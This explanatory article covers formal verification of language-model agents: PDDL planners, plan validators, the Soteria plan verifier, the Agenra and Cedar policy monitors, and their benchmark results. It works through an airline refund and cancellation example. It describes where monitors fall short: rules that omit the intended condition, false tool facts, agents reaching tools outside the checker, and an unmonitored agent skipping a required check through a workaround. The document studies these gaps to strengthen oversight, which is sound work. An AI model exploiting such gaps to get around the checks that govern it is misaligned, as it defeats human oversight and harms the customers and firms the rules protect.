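# Do formal planners and symbolic checkers make language-model agents verifiable?

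## What a formal guarantee says and what it depends on

Formal verification means proving mathematically that a system meets a precisely written requirement. Engineers use it on aircraft, medical devices and other equipment that must not fail. In the past few years, researchers have tried to apply it to language-model agents, in which a large language model decides step by step what to do. Nobody knows how to prove much about the model itself, so most of this work leaves the model unchanged and puts a conventional program, called a checker, around it. The checker holds rules written in a formal language and accepts or rejects what the agent proposes. Developers then claim a guarantee that the accepted actions obey the rules, whatever the model does.

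The claim is often true, but its value depends on where the rules came from. In many of these systems, an unverified language model wrote the first draft of the rules.

### Agents, planners, solvers and monitors

An agent is a language model that pursues a task over several steps by calling tools, which are outside software such as a booking system. A tool call is a single request to a tool, with its arguments, such as `cancel_reservation("RES123")`. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes the cycle in four steps. The model produces text, the surrounding software extracts a tool call from it, the tool runs, and its output goes back into the model's input. A checker can intervene after the call is extracted and before the tool runs.

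The example from here on is an airline's customer-service agent. *τ²-Bench* (Barres, Dong and colleagues, 2025), a set of simulated customer-service tasks, gives the agent a written policy of a few pages. The policy forbids the agent to cancel a booking once the customer has flown any part of it. The booking software does not enforce this rule. The policy states that "the API does not check that cancellation rules are met", so a prohibited cancellation goes through.

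A planner is a search program. Its input is a formal description of the starting situation, the goal and the available actions, and its output is a sequence of actions that leads from the start to the goal. The standard language for such descriptions is PDDL, the Planning Domain Definition Language. In PDDL the cancellation could look like this:

```
(:action cancel
  :parameters (?b - booking)
  :precondition (and (active ?b) (checked-unflown ?b))
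  :effect (and (cancelled ?b) (not (active ?b))))
```

Suppose a status check is the only action with the effect `checked-unflown`. A planner that starts from an active booking and aims for a cancelled one will then return two steps, the check and the cancellation. It cannot return the cancellation alone, because the precondition would fail. (Actions in basic PDDL have fixed effects, so this little model takes for granted that the check comes out well.)

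An SMT (satisfiability modulo theories) solver decides whether a set of logical formulas over numbers, Booleans and similar types can all be true together. In *The Fusion of Large Language Models and Formal Methods*, Zhang, Cai and colleagues (2024) had a language model translate a scheduling request into formulas for the SMT solver Z3. The task was to find a day when David (free Monday or Tuesday), Emma (free Tuesday or Wednesday) and Alex (free Tuesday or Thursday) could all meet. The model's first translation stated when each person was free but not when each was busy, so the formulas allowed a solution in which all three were free on Monday. After the model added the missing statements, Tuesday was the only solution. Z3 was right about the formulas both times, but only the second set matched the request.

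Temporal logic adds operators for order in time, such as "always", "eventually" and "until". A typical rule is "no cancellation until a status check has come back clean". In *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) reviewed 38 studies on specifying and verifying agents and found that 13 were based on temporal logic, more than on any other formalism. Kamath and colleagues offer developers an easier notation for the same kind of rule. With its `Before` form, for example, a developer can require an agent to open a file before reading it, with the same file name in both calls.

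A monitor is a checker that inspects each tool call before it runs and can block it. If the airline agent proposes a cancellation without first checking the status, the monitor blocks the call and returns a reason, and the model has to try something else. Some developers use a second language model as the monitor, which is easier to set up but less dependable. Kamath and colleagues describe a retail test in which a customer wanted to return a camera. Although DynaGuard, a monitor of this kind, was checking the agent's actions, the agent fetched and disclosed the order details without authenticating the customer. A symbolic monitor enforcing the rule "authenticate first" would have blocked that lookup every time.

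### The airline rule as a formula

To write the cancellation rule formally, one needs something for the formula to be about. The usual choice is the trace: the list of tool calls so far, each with its arguments and its result. The formula below follows He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *SOTERIA*, a system for planning and monitoring agents, with the names spelled out:

$$\forall c \in \text{Cancel}\;\; \exists k \in \text{NoFlown}:\quad k \prec c \;\wedge\; k.\text{booking} = c.\text{booking} \;\wedge\; k.\text{result} = \text{true}$$

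For every cancellation $c$ in the trace, an earlier ($\prec$) flown-status check $k$ on the same booking must have returned "true", meaning that it found no flown flights.

A monitor applies the formula by adding the proposed call to the trace and checking whether the formula holds. Suppose the agent first looks up booking RES123. The rule does not mention lookups, so the call runs. Next the agent tries to cancel. The extended trace contains a cancellation and no status check, so the formula is false and the monitor blocks the call. The agent runs the check, gets "true", and tries again. This time the formula holds and the cancellation goes through.

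Even this short formula differs from the English in a few places. Once a check has found no flown flights, the formula stays satisfied, even if the first flight leaves before the agent cancels the booking. This can't happen in the benchmark, whose policy fixes the current time at 3 p.m. on 15 May 2024, but it could at a real airline. The English policy also requires the agent to hand a partly flown booking over to a human colleague, which the formula leaves out. Finally, the meaning of "flown" depends on how the status tool is programmed. The policy lists "flying" as a status for flights that have taken off but not yet landed, without specifying whether they count as flown. The tool's programmer has to decide, and that choice can't be determined from a proof about the formula.

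### What the guarantee states

Write $\Phi$ for the rules, $\sigma$ for the trace so far and $a$ for a proposed call. The property that a monitor needs is

$$\sigma \models \Phi \;\text{ and the monitor accepts } a \;\;\Longrightarrow\;\; \sigma \cdot a \models \Phi$$

where $\models$ means "satisfies" and $\sigma \cdot a$ is the trace with $a$ added. The empty trace satisfies the airline rule, since it contains no cancellations. If every accepted call preserves the rule, then by induction the rule holds for the whole run, however long. In words: given these rules and these facts, every accepted action satisfies the rules. The "facts" are the recorded results of earlier calls and whatever else the monitor reads from databases.

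The main attraction of the approach is that this argument does not depend on the language model. The conclusion holds even if the model is bad or has just read an attacker's instructions in an email.

The induction covers what the literature calls safety rules, which a bad call breaks permanently. It does not cover a rule such as "After writing a file, read it back." Right after the write, the agent has not yet met this requirement, but it has not broken it either, so blocking the write would make no sense. He and colleagues have their monitor check such obligations when the task ends. By then it can detect a missing step, but there is no offending call left to block.

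A checker is logically sound if it never accepts what its formal rules forbid, and complete if it never rejects what they allow. Soundness alone does not make a checker useful, because a monitor that blocks every call, including the permitted ones, is sound.

The monitor for the flown-status rule can easily be both sound and complete, because it only has to check a finite list. For harder questions, designers usually keep soundness and give up some completeness. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) presents a permission monitor for agents and a test for changes to the permission list. The test is meant to prove that every workflow the old list allowed is still allowed under the new one. On 51 changes written for the paper by its authors, the structural version of the test certified 16 of the 21 harmless changes and none of the 30 harmful ones. It could not find a proof for the other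 five harmless changes, which a more general method certified. A rejection from a sound but incomplete checker therefore means only that the checker found no proof, and the rejected change may still be harmless.

### Four links

The guarantee holds only "given these rules and these facts." For the proof to apply to a customer's booking, four things must hold, and any one of them can fail while the other three hold.

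| Link | How it could fail at the airline | What usually supports it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The rules say what people meant | The airline wanted to include flights in the air, and the rule covers only landed ones | A language model's draft, with or without human review |
| The facts given to the checker are true | The status tool returns "no flown flights" for a half-used ticket | Trust in databases and tools, sometimes in a language model's reading of a text |
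| The checker is correct | A bug in comparing booking numbers lets a check on one booking unlock another | Proof, or ordinary testing |
| Every action passes through the checker | The agent also has a terminal and edits the booking database directly | Access control and careful engineering |

Agenra's proofs concern the correctness of its checker. The core is written in Lean, a language in which programmers can write a program together with machine-checked proofs about it. Shivakumar and colleagues prove several properties, including that no permission exceeds its usage limit and that every admitted action falls within both the user's permissions and the application's own ceiling. They state that they trust the Lean compiler, its runtime, and the Python code that translates policies and passes calls to the core without proof, and that the theorems assume one call at a time. These limits are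 neither unusual nor alarming, but "a verified monitor" generally means a verified core with unverified software on both sides.

Agenra assumes that every action passes through the checker. The barrier between agent and monitor consists of Python objects inside a single process, and Agenra notes that this does not isolate arbitrary Python code. The barrier should hold against an agent that can only propose calls, but an agent with permission to run its own scripts in the same process might get around it.

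The facts a checker uses come mostly from ordinary software. In an example from Shivakumar and colleagues, a monitor follows its rule exactly, but a report still goes to the wrong person because somebody has tampered with the directory that supplies the address. Other facts exist only in the conversation. Under the airline's policy, the agent must find out why the customer wants to cancel, and the insurance covers health and weather but not a change of plans. No database records whether the customer is ill, so the language model fills in the answer from what the customer says. A checker might then treat as given a fact that came from a learned model.

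Finally, the guarantee depends on the rules, which are written mostly by learned models. He and colleagues checked theirs more carefully than most. A language model drafted formal rules from the policy and the tool descriptions, and the researchers then went through the policy clause by clause, correcting and adding rules. This took a few hours per benchmark and produced 24 formulas for the airline. The review still missed some mistakes, and they report correcting wrongly encoded rules and adding missing ones later, while auditing the results.

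At least one discrepancy seems to remain in the published list. The English policy lets an insured customer cancel if the insurance covers the reason, but the formula, as printed, requires only that the booking have insurance. An insured customer who cancels merely because of a change of plans satisfies the formula but not the policy, and a monitor enforcing the formula would allow the cancellation and record no violation. Dantas and colleagues use the term "false assurance" for the general problem of a verifier finding no violation because the formula omits the condition that was violated.

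Better translation would not remove the difficulty entirely, because the English may not determine a single rule. *Policy Loopholes in Agent Evaluation* (Cao, 2026) audited the same airline policy and found 15 places where it is incomplete, ambiguous or contradictory. For example, passengers on basic economy, the cheapest fare, cannot change flights, but they can change cabin, and passengers in other cabins can change flights. The policy does not specify whether an agent may upgrade the cabin first and then change the flight. In a later release of the benchmark, τ³-bench, the maintainers allowed this in one task and refused it in another, without changing the clause.

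Deciding what counts as a loophole takes judgement, and this was one author's audit. Still, the maintainers had independently revised all seven tasks that Cao found affected, which is some evidence that the gaps are real. Anyone who turns such a clause into a formula has to pick a reading, and the proof is then about that reading.

### Three senses of "verifiable"

People who call an agent "verifiable" can mean any of three things, and much confusion arises when they prove one but claim another.

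A formal guarantee may mean that the checker is correct: it accepts and rejects exactly as its specification requires, or at least never accepts what it should reject. This is a theorem about the program that holds whatever rules are loaded into it, so it doesn't show that the rules are adequate. *Agenra* illustrates this with three policies, and the checker is equally correct under all of them. In the example, an agent is supposed to send Alice the public parts of a private report, once. The first policy would also have let the agent send her any other public text. The second adds a rule that the message must come out of the tool that strips confidential fields, but an attacker's text could still go through that tool, pass the monitor and use up the single permitted release. The third closes this gap by adding a rule on the tool's input.

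Calling an agent verifiable may mean that its actions satisfy the formal rules. If the checker is correct and every action passes through it, developers can truthfully report that no run broke a rule. The airline rule covers only recorded results, so if the status tool returns a wrong answer, the agent can cancel a half-flown booking and the trace will still satisfy the rule.

Or they may mean that the agent's behaviour is what people wanted. This requires all four links, and the agent must also get the work done, since an agent that does nothing will rarely break a prohibition. Customers and airlines care about this sense, but it is also the hardest to prove. A proposal known as guaranteed safe AI aims to do so.

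In one run recorded by He and colleagues, a customer asked an agent with no monitor to cancel two bookings. The agent upgraded one to business class, which the policy lets customers cancel, and then cancelled both without checking whether any of the flights had already been flown. The benchmark's automatic scorer gave the run full marks because cancellation was the expected outcome. But He and colleagues count two violations, the missing check and the upgrade, which they describe as a workaround that the policy does not permit.

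Their monitor would have caught the missing check. But as printed, their cancellation and modification rules would accept the upgrade if the agent ran the status check and looked the booking up again before cancelling, because a business cabin on record is enough. The English policy allows cabin changes on unflown bookings and cancellation in business class, but it doesn't mention changing cabin in order to cancel. The corrected run therefore satisfies the formal rules. Only the airline can decide whether it wanted to allow this, and the written policy suggests that nobody there had thought about it.

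## Planners and plan checkers that work with a language model

A monitor checks one tool call at a time. It can block a forbidden cancellation, but it cannot determine whether the agent's next five steps lead toward its goal, or what the agent should try after a block. Researchers address these questions by checking a whole plan before the agent acts on it. Their systems differ mainly in what the language model writes. The model writes a description of the problem in LLM+P and the plan itself in LLM-Modulo. In Soteria, it drafts the rules the plan must obey and then writes a plan with branches.

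### LLM+P: the model describes the problem

Liu, Jiang and colleagues (2023) observed in *LLM+P* that GPT-4 was bad at planning but good at translating, so they had it translate the user's request into PDDL and used a formal planner to produce the plan.

PDDL splits a planning problem into two files. The domain file lists the actions, such as the airline's `cancel` action, with their preconditions and effects. The problem file lists the objects, the starting situation and the goal. In LLM+P, a human expert writes the domain file once, and the language model writes a new problem file for each request. The planner Fast Downward then searches for a plan, and the language model turns the result back into English.

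One problem from Liu and colleagues starts with five blocks in a stack, which from bottom to top are b1, b2, b4, b3 and b5. The goal is to have b1 on b2, b3 on b5 and b4 on b1. Each block can have at most one other block directly on top of it, but GPT-4's own plan put b3 on b5 and, two steps later, b2 on b5 as well. When asked to write a problem file for the planner Fast Downward instead, GPT-4 used a made-up predicate, `empty`, and left out that b1 is on the table. Liu and colleagues then added an example to the prompt, a different stack of blocks with its correct problem file. GPT-4 then wrote a usable file, and Fast Downward returned a correct plan of twelve steps.

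The full test had 20 tasks in each of seven domains. GPT-4, planning directly with a worked example in the prompt, found a correct plan for 30% of the block-stacking tasks, 25% of the crate-storage tasks and none of the bartending tasks. LLM+P solved 90%, 85% and 100% of these, respectively. But it solved only 20% of the tasks in Termes, a construction domain, and none in Floortile, where robots paint a grid of tiles. Most failures came from errors in the problem files. In Floortile, GPT-4 left out facts about which tiles are connected, so no plan existed. Without the worked example, LLM+P solved no tasks in any domain.

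Fast Downward is sound, so any plan it returns is valid for the two files. One setting also guarantees an optimal plan if it finishes. In the bartending tasks, that setting finished within the 200-second limit only 20% of the time, and the 100% figure comes from a faster setting without that guarantee. Neither property covers the translation of the user's English into the problem file. The Floortile errors were at least visible, because the planner returned no plan.

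### LLM-Modulo: the model proposes and critics reject

Kambhampati, Valmeekam and colleagues (2024) objected in *Position* that systems like LLM+P treat language models as "glorified translators". Such systems also inherit the planner's limits, since the user's problem has to fit into the planner's language and the search can take too long. Kambhampati and colleagues instead proposed LLM-Modulo, in which the language model writes the plan and a set of programs called critics test it.

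Hard critics test correctness, for example whether each action is possible when it is reached, or whether the plan stays within a budget. Soft critics, which may be language models, evaluate style and preferences. For PDDL plans, the hard critic can be VAL, a standard validator. VAL starts from the initial state, checks each action's preconditions, applies its effects, and checks the goal at the end. Validating a plan is much easier than finding one, because a validator follows a single sequence of actions, while a planner may have to search through an enormous number of them.

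If a critic finds a problem, a controller adds the critic's feedback to the next prompt, and the model tries again. The feedback can range from "wrong" to a full list of errors with a suggested repair. The loop ends when every hard critic accepts the plan or the budget runs out.

The loop returns a plan only if the hard critics accept it, so it is as sound as they are, however poor the model. It would be just as sound with a generator of random strings in place of the model, although it would almost never return a plan. The model therefore determines how often the loop succeeds. The loop cannot show that a problem has no solution, whereas a complete planner can, given enough time.

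Kambhampati and colleagues insisted on external critics because of experiments in which GPT-4 criticised its own answers. One of the tasks was graph colouring, where neighbouring points in a network must get different colours. Self-criticism gave worse results than taking the first answer. GPT-4 failed to recognise that some of its colourings were correct, kept revising them, and ended with wrong ones.

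With VAL as the critic for up to 15 rounds, the language model's success rate rose to 82% in Blocksworld, the block-stacking domain, and to 70% in a logistics domain. It reached only about 10% in a version of Blocksworld with disguised names. Kambhampati and colleagues point out that even there, any plan the system produced had passed VAL and was "guaranteed correct by its model". "Model" here means the formal description of the domain. They propose that a language model help draft this description and that a human expert criticise and approve it.

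They also keep people out of the inner loop. A person who keeps prompting until the plan looks right may unknowingly supply the answer, as the questioners of Clever Hans did for the horse that seemed to do arithmetic. People take part once per domain, to approve the description, and once per problem, to complete the request.

The language model can also help build the critics. In a travel-planning test, Kambhampati and colleagues had the model list the kinds of critic the task needed, with light human supervision, and found that language models could write the code for several critics, including hard critics. The loop improved results to about six times the baseline, which was 0.7% for GPT-3.5 Turbo. But a hard critic is sound only if its code is correct. If a language model writes that code, then unless someone proves it correct or reviews it carefully, the guarantee depends on the same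 kind of model that the critic is meant to check.

### The claim that language models cannot plan

The subtitle of the LLM-Modulo paper begins "LLMs Can't Plan", and in 2024 the evidence for this was good. Much of it came from PlanBench, a test suite by members of the same research group. Its best-known part has 600 Blocksworld problems, which involve three to five blocks and take 2 to 16 steps to solve. A second version, Mystery Blocksworld, has the same problems but gives the actions and objects misleading names, which makes no difference to a planner. When the prompt included an example, GPT-4 solved about 34% of the ordinary problems and 4% of the disguised ones. Kambhampati and colleagues concluded that such models mostly retrieve plans that resemble ones they have seen.

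OpenAI's o1-preview, the first of its models trained to reason at length before answering, weakened the claim within months. In Valmeekam, Stechly and colleagues (2024), in *Planning in Strawberry Fields*, it solved 97.8% of the ordinary problems and 52.8% of the disguised ones. It did much worse on 110 harder Blocksworld problems, with 6 to 20 blocks and at least 20 steps. Valmeekam and colleagues then put o1-preview in a loop with a sound verifier, for at most ten rounds:

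| Problem set | Tasks | o1-preview alone | With a verifier |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Blocksworld, 20 steps or more | 110 | 23.65% | 98.2% |
| Graph colouring, 20 points | 50 | 64% | 94% |
| Sokoban, a box-pushing puzzle | 55 | 12.7% | 43.6% |
| Travel planning | 180 | 10% | 65% |
| Trip planning, 10 cities | 200 | 4% | 15.5% |

A verifier can only accept or reject a plan, and perhaps explain why. The model, o1-preview, still had to find the plans, and it never did in more than half of the Sokoban tasks. The loop also raised the cost of the hard Blocksworld set from \$52 to \$139. Fast Downward solved every problem in the standard 600-problem set, at about 0.12 seconds each on a personal computer.

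Valmeekam and colleagues also gave o1-preview 100 Blocksworld problems with impossible goals. It recognised 27 as impossible and produced a full plan for 54. A validator would have rejected all 54 plans before execution.

These results are out of date, because the newest models have largely solved problems of the PlanBench type. In *End-to-end PDDL Planning with Hardcoded and Dynamic Agents* (2025), Gemini 3 Flash, a small and fast model, averaged about 97% without help on four PlanBench datasets, including disguised versions of Blocksworld and logistics. *Verifiable Efficiency Limits of Innate LLM Planning in Sliding Puzzles* (2026) tested newer models on sliding-block boards. OpenAI's Astra and Anthropic's Fable 5 and Opus 5.5 each completed the board in all 960 attempts, with no illegal plans. Smaller models did worse, down to 56% for Haiku 4.5. Even the best models planned inefficiently,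 and only 27% of Astra's plans were as short as possible.

*Frontier Large Language Models Rival State-of-the-Art Planners* (Corrêa, Pereira and Seipp, 2025) makes a harder comparison, using 360 newly generated tasks in eight domains from the 2023 International Planning Competition. The Blocksworld tasks had up to 477 blocks, and some plans had more than 1,000 steps. Each planner got 30 minutes per task on one processor core. Gemini 3.1 Pro solved 245 tasks, compared with 234 for the best planner, Scorpion Maidu, and none for GPT-3.5.

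When Corrêa and colleagues replaced all names with random strings, Gemini 3.1 Pro still solved 231 tasks. Its reasoning showed that it often recognised four of the domains, such as Sokoban, from their structure, so memory may have helped there. But in the four domains it never recognised, it solved only seven fewer tasks in total than with the original names. This is evidence against the idea that it retrieves old plans by their wording.

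### Why check a model that plans well

Part of the original case for these systems no longer holds. In 2023 the planner gave GPT-4 an ability it lacked. For Gemini 3 Flash on PlanBench, going through PDDL changed the average by 0.1 percentage points, according to *End-to-end PDDL Planning with Hardcoded and Dynamic Agents*. Adding a translation step to such a model risks errors like those in Floortile and solves almost no additional problems. GPT-5.4 did benefit. It was much worse alone, and with the PDDL pipeline it solved every task in three of the four datasets. A planner is also far cheaper to run than a language model, whichever solves more.

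The case for a guarantee holds even when a language model scores well. Even 960 successes in 960 attempts are compatible with a failure rate of about 0.3% on similar boards (at 95% confidence, treating the attempts as independent), and they tell us little about requests that an attacker has designed. VAL, by contrast, checks the particular plan it is given. Corrêa and colleagues' best model outscored the planners, but they still ran its plans through VAL and discarded any that failed, because a language model alone does not guarantee that its plans are valid.

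A model can plan well and still break the rules. An illegal move gains nothing in a sliding puzzle, but an airline agent has customers who want things that the policy forbids, and the booking software lets it skip the flown-status check. Skipping the check isn't a planning error, since the cancellation goes through faster without it. In experiments by He and colleagues, Claude Opus 4.6 with no guardrail broke at least one formal rule in 18% of the airline tasks. It ran at a low reasoning setting, and stronger models have come out since, so the current figure may well be lower. Even so, a better score on PlanBench would not rule out errors of this kind.

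### Soteria: a plan verified before any tool runs

In Soteria, published in November 2026, a verifier checks the model's plan before the agent makes its first tool call. Each tool has a contract that describes what it does, with a precondition on its inputs and a postcondition on its outputs. For a payment tool, the precondition might be a positive amount and a valid payment method, and the postcondition might be a confirmation number. As with the policy rules, a language model drafts the contracts and people validate them by hand.

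The model writes its plan as a guarded transition system, which is a flowchart with exact semantics. Each state is a stage of the procedure. Each transition leads to another state, makes at most one tool call, and may have a guard, which is a condition on the data collected so far. An example from He and colleagues is a plan for "Cancel reservation RES123". The policy in the example requires the agent to verify that no flights have been flown and requires the booking to be at most 24 hours old.

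| State | What the plan does | Facts established so far |
| --- | --- | --- |
| LOOKUP | Fetches the booking | `resv` satisfies the lookup tool's postcondition |
| CHECK_AGE | Computes the hours since booking | The above, and `hrs` satisfies the time tool's postcondition |
| CHECK_RULES | Goes to DO_CANCEL if `hrs` ≤ 24, otherwise to NOT_PERMITTED | The above, and on the way to DO_CANCEL, `hrs` ≤ 24 |
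| DO_CANCEL | Cancels the booking and ends in DONE | The above, and the result satisfies the cancellation tool's postcondition |

The plan looks sensible, but it never checks whether the customer has flown.

The right-hand column is the symbolic state. It is a formula that covers every combination of values the plan's variables could have at that point, whatever the tools return within their contracts. Write $\Sigma(s)$ for the symbolic state at $s$. Along a transition from $s$ to $s'$ with guard $g$, it becomes

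$$\Sigma_{s \to s'} = \delta(\Sigma(s) \wedge g)$$

where $\delta$ adds what the transition establishes, such as the postcondition of the tool it calls. If several transitions lead to the same state, the verifier joins their formulas with "or".

Soteria hands the resulting proof obligations to Dafny, an automated program verifier that uses an SMT solver internally. For tool contracts, Dafny must prove that every call satisfies its precondition:

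$$\Sigma(s) \wedge g \Rightarrow P_a(\vec{v})$$

Here $P_a$ is the precondition of tool $a$, and $\vec{v}$ are the arguments of the call. For example, the facts established at DO_CANCEL must imply the cancellation tool's precondition before the plan may call that tool.

Progress means that the plan cannot get stuck. Every state before the end must be reachable for at least some values, and the guards leaving it must cover all the values that can occur there:

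$$\Sigma(s) \Rightarrow g_1 \vee \dots \vee g_n$$

The example passes because `hrs` is either at most 24 or more than 24. If the guards were "less than 24" and "more than 24", a booking exactly 24 hours old would match neither, and the check would fail.

The policy rules concern the order of tool calls, which the values of variables alone don't show, so Soteria adds records that exist only inside the proof. A counter numbers the steps, and each tool mentioned in the rules has a log of its calls, with their arguments and results. A third record tracks which tool results went into each variable, for rules such as "the refund amount must come from the booking". Dafny must prove that these records satisfy all the rules at every end state.

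In the example, the flown-status rule holds at NOT_PERMITTED because the plan has cancelled nothing on that path. At DONE, the cancellation log has one entry and the log of flown-status checks is empty. The rule requires an earlier successful check for every cancellation, so the proof fails. Soteria rejects the plan before any tool runs and reports the broken rule to the model, which tries again.

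To follow the rule, the plan must make the missing call and cancel only if the check returns "true". If the plan added the call without branching on the result, it would still cancel when the check returned "false". Soteria is stricter in this respect than the PDDL planner. The planner found a sequence of actions for one fully described situation, while Dafny has to cover every result that the tools' contracts allow.

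The model gets up to eight retries. If no attempt passes in full, Soteria uses the best partly verified plan. To keep plans short, Soteria supplies a library of verified sub-plans that a larger plan can call like tools for standard procedures such as cancelling. On the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini, Dafny verified 65 of 68 plans with this library and 38 of 60 without it.

It can do so because of the monitor. A second language-model process, the executor, carries out the task. It receives the plan as a flowchart that shrinks as results come in, but it can call any tool. After the monitor blocks a call, the executor can look up which steps remain. A separate strict mode allows only the calls that a fully verified plan permits at that moment. If a customer asks in passing about a second booking, strict mode would block the harmless lookup that the usual mode allows.

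The proof about the plan assumes that the contracts describe the tools correctly. If a tool returns a result that violates its postcondition, Soteria aborts the run, since the proof no longer applies. Soteria does not detect a wrong answer that has the right form.

### What Soteria's 100% measures

He and colleagues tested Soteria on 207 tasks: 50 airline and 114 retail tasks from *τ²-Bench*, and 43 from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long tasks with files and other software. They used four language models: GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Claude Opus 4.6. Soteria reached 100% conformance on all three benchmarks with every model. The four baselines (no guardrail, a language model as judge, and two rule-based monitors) reached at most 93%. Soteria's task success averaged 1.7 times that of the best baseline.

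Conformance here means that a run broke none of the 98 formulas that He and colleagues wrote for the three benchmarks. The monitor blocks any call that would break one of these formulas, so the result would be 100% even if the executor picked its calls at random. The figure is good evidence that the monitor has no serious bugs, but not that the formulas match the policies. For that, one has to rely on a clause-by-clause check done by hand, which covered only rules that govern changes to data and that a monitor can enforce from the record of tool calls.

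This argument does not apply to a few formulas. Two of the 41 for Toolathlon require the agent to read a file back after writing or editing it. Blocking cannot enforce that, so the absence of violations of these two formulas reflects how the agents behaved when they followed verified plans.

He and colleagues also added Soteria's components one at a time on the airline tasks. With GPT-5.4-mini and an unverified plan, 74% of runs conformed. Verifying the plans raised this to 80%, adding sub-plans didn't change it, and adding the monitor raised it to 100%. With Gemini 3 Flash, the corresponding figures were 54%, 56%, 58% and 100%. Verifying the plan did little to make the executor obey the rules, presumably because the executor was free to depart from the plan.

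The plans seem to matter more for getting the work done. With no guardrail, Claude Opus 4.6 often collected all the information for a retail request and then passed the customer to a human. It made the expected change in only 57% of the tasks that required one. With a plan that specified which change to make and when, it made the change every time. Its success rate on the retail tasks was 90.4%, against 46.5% for the best baseline, though much of that gain has little to do with verification.

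The factor of 1.7 also depends on the scoring. A run counts as a success only if the agent completed the task and broke none of the formulas, so the baselines lose credit for breaking rules that Soteria enforces on its own runs. Averaged over the twelve combinations of model and benchmark, Soteria succeeded in about 47% of tasks and the best baselines in about 27%. Ignoring violations and taking the baseline that completed the most tasks in each combination raises the baselines' average to about 40% and lowers the factor to about 1.2. On Toolathlon, Haiku 4.5 and Opus 4.6 completed fewer tasks with Soteria than with no guardrail.

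The stricter score is reasonable, because an airline would be right to count a prohibited cancellation as a failure. But its reliability depends on the quality of the formulas. AgentSpec, one of the rule-based monitors, ran the same rules converted into its own format and still let through 7 to 37 violations per combination, so the format probably could not express all of the rules.

The main results come from one attempt per task. He and colleagues repeated the airline tasks five times with GPT-5.4-mini, allowing only three planning retries to save money. Conformance was 100% in every run, by design. Task success averaged 50.8%, against 48.0% for AgentSpec, with overlapping confidence intervals. Soteria's advantage over a good monitor is therefore uncertain for this model when retries are few. Soteria also cost more than any baseline in the customer-service tasks, because the model writes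 a new plan at each turn of the conversation. With Opus 4.6, an airline task cost \$0.80, compared with \$0.32 without a guardrail.

### A valid plan for the wrong problem

LLM+P, LLM-Modulo and Soteria all accept a valid plan for a wrongly described problem. For example, the airline's `cancel` action in PDDL has the precondition `checked-unflown`. Suppose a customer writes that they have not flown yet, and the language model adds `(checked-unflown RES123)` to the starting facts without checking. Fast Downward will then return a plan with one step, the cancellation. If the language model proposes this plan in LLM-Modulo and VAL uses the same files, VAL will accept it, because the plan is valid for the problem those files describe.

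This mistake is harder to notice than the ones in Floortile, where the description left out something true and the planner could not find a plan. When a description allows too much, the planner still finds a plan, and that plan looks like any other. The fraction of problems for which a planner finds a plan is therefore a poor measure of how often the translation is faithful.

A description can also be correct but omit something that matters. In *The Curious Case of Planning for Unreliable Agents*, Daneshi, Patra and colleagues had a PDDL planner direct language-model agents that booked flights, hotels and taxis. The planner worked with places and modes of transport and left details such as prices and times to the agents. An agent could complete its booking and still contradict the plan or make the schedule impossible, mainly because the PDDL description did not contain those details. Daneshi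 and colleagues added a module that looks for such conflicts after each booking, updates the PDDL description and plans again. A language-model agent performs the update, and the researchers warn that agents may report the state of the world wrongly.

The same thing can happen with Soteria's formal rule that accepts any insured booking, whatever the customer's reason for cancelling, even though Soteria has richer descriptions and people have reviewed its rules. A longer version of the example plan requires the reason to be health or weather. Dafny rejected that plan because it lacked the flown-status check. If the model added the check but dropped the condition about the reason, Dafny would verify the new plan and the monitor would not flag it.

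## Policy engines that check each tool call

Much of the work in Soteria, a research system, goes into writing and verifying plans. The products that companies can already deploy leave out the plan and keep the monitor. Amazon Web Services (AWS) introduced one in December 2025 for AgentCore, its service for running agents. According to AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now includes Policy (preview), Evaluations (preview) and more* (2025), the product intercepts every tool call in real time and checks the call against rules that a team can write in ordinary English.

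### A gateway and a refund rule

In AgentCore, a gateway between the agent and its tools passes each call to a policy engine, an ordinary program that checks the call against written rules. The gateway forwards the call to the tool only if the engine returns "allow". AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* justifies this placement by treating the language model as an untrusted actor. An attacker can hide instructions in an email or a tool's output (a prompt injection), and the model may follow them, so the rules must be kept where the model's text cannot change them.

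The rules are in Cedar, an open-source language that AWS developed for authorization. An application that uses Cedar asks one question, "Is this request authorized?", and gets back "allow" or "deny". David Richardson, the AWS vice president for AgentCore, gave VentureBeat the example of a customer-service agent that may refund up to $100 and must pass larger requests to a human. The first half of that rule could look like this in Cedar:

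```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"ProcessRefund",
  resource
)
when { context.input.refundAmount <= 100 };
```

The principal is the signed-in user the agent acts for, the action is the tool, and the resource is the gateway. `context.input` holds the tool call's arguments.

Suppose the agent proposes a refund of $80. The engine finds a `permit` rule that lets this kind of user use this tool for refunds of up to $100, so the gateway forwards the call and the customer gets the money. Next the agent proposes $250, perhaps because a customer insisted that the airline owes that much. This exceeds the limit, so the rule doesn't apply. No other rule permits the call, so the engine denies it.

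The second call fails because no rule mentions refunds above $100, and Cedar denies any call that no rule permits. If a colleague later adds a `permit` for refunds up to $500, the $250 refund goes through. To make $100 a firm limit, the policy's author has to add a `forbid` rule for anything larger, because a matching `forbid` overrides every `permit`, regardless of the order of the rules.

The other half of Richardson's rule is harder to enforce. The engine can refuse the $250 refund, but it can't make the model then pass the customer to a human.

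AgentCore also applies the rules before the agent proposes a tool call. When the agent requests the list of tools, the gateway omits any that the policy would deny regardless of the arguments. If the refund rule were the only one in force, the list would contain only one tool.

Cedar has no loops and keeps no memory between requests, so the engine usually answers in time proportional to the size of the input. There is also better evidence that its checker is correct than there is for most software. Its maintainers describe Cedar as the first policy language designed from the start for formal verification, and they also use differential random testing, in which they feed the same random inputs to two implementations and compare the answers.

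### What a solver can prove before any call

Cedar policies are simple enough that a program can translate one into a formula about a single request and pass it to an SMT solver. AWS's tool for this, Cedar Analysis, checks for several kinds of mistake before the policy takes effect.

A rule may be impossible to satisfy. In one of AWS's examples, the author wants to allow refunds for gold and platinum customers but writes "and" instead of "or", so the rule applies only to customers in both tiers. The solver finds no request that satisfies the rule. The opposite mistake is a condition that is always true, such as "the quantity is at least 100 or less than 100".

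Two rules may also conflict. Another pair of AWS's rules permits refunds under \$100 for gold customers and forbids refunds under \$500 for gold and platinum customers. With $t$ for the customer's tier and $x$ for the amount, the solver looks for a refund that the first rule permits and the second does not block:
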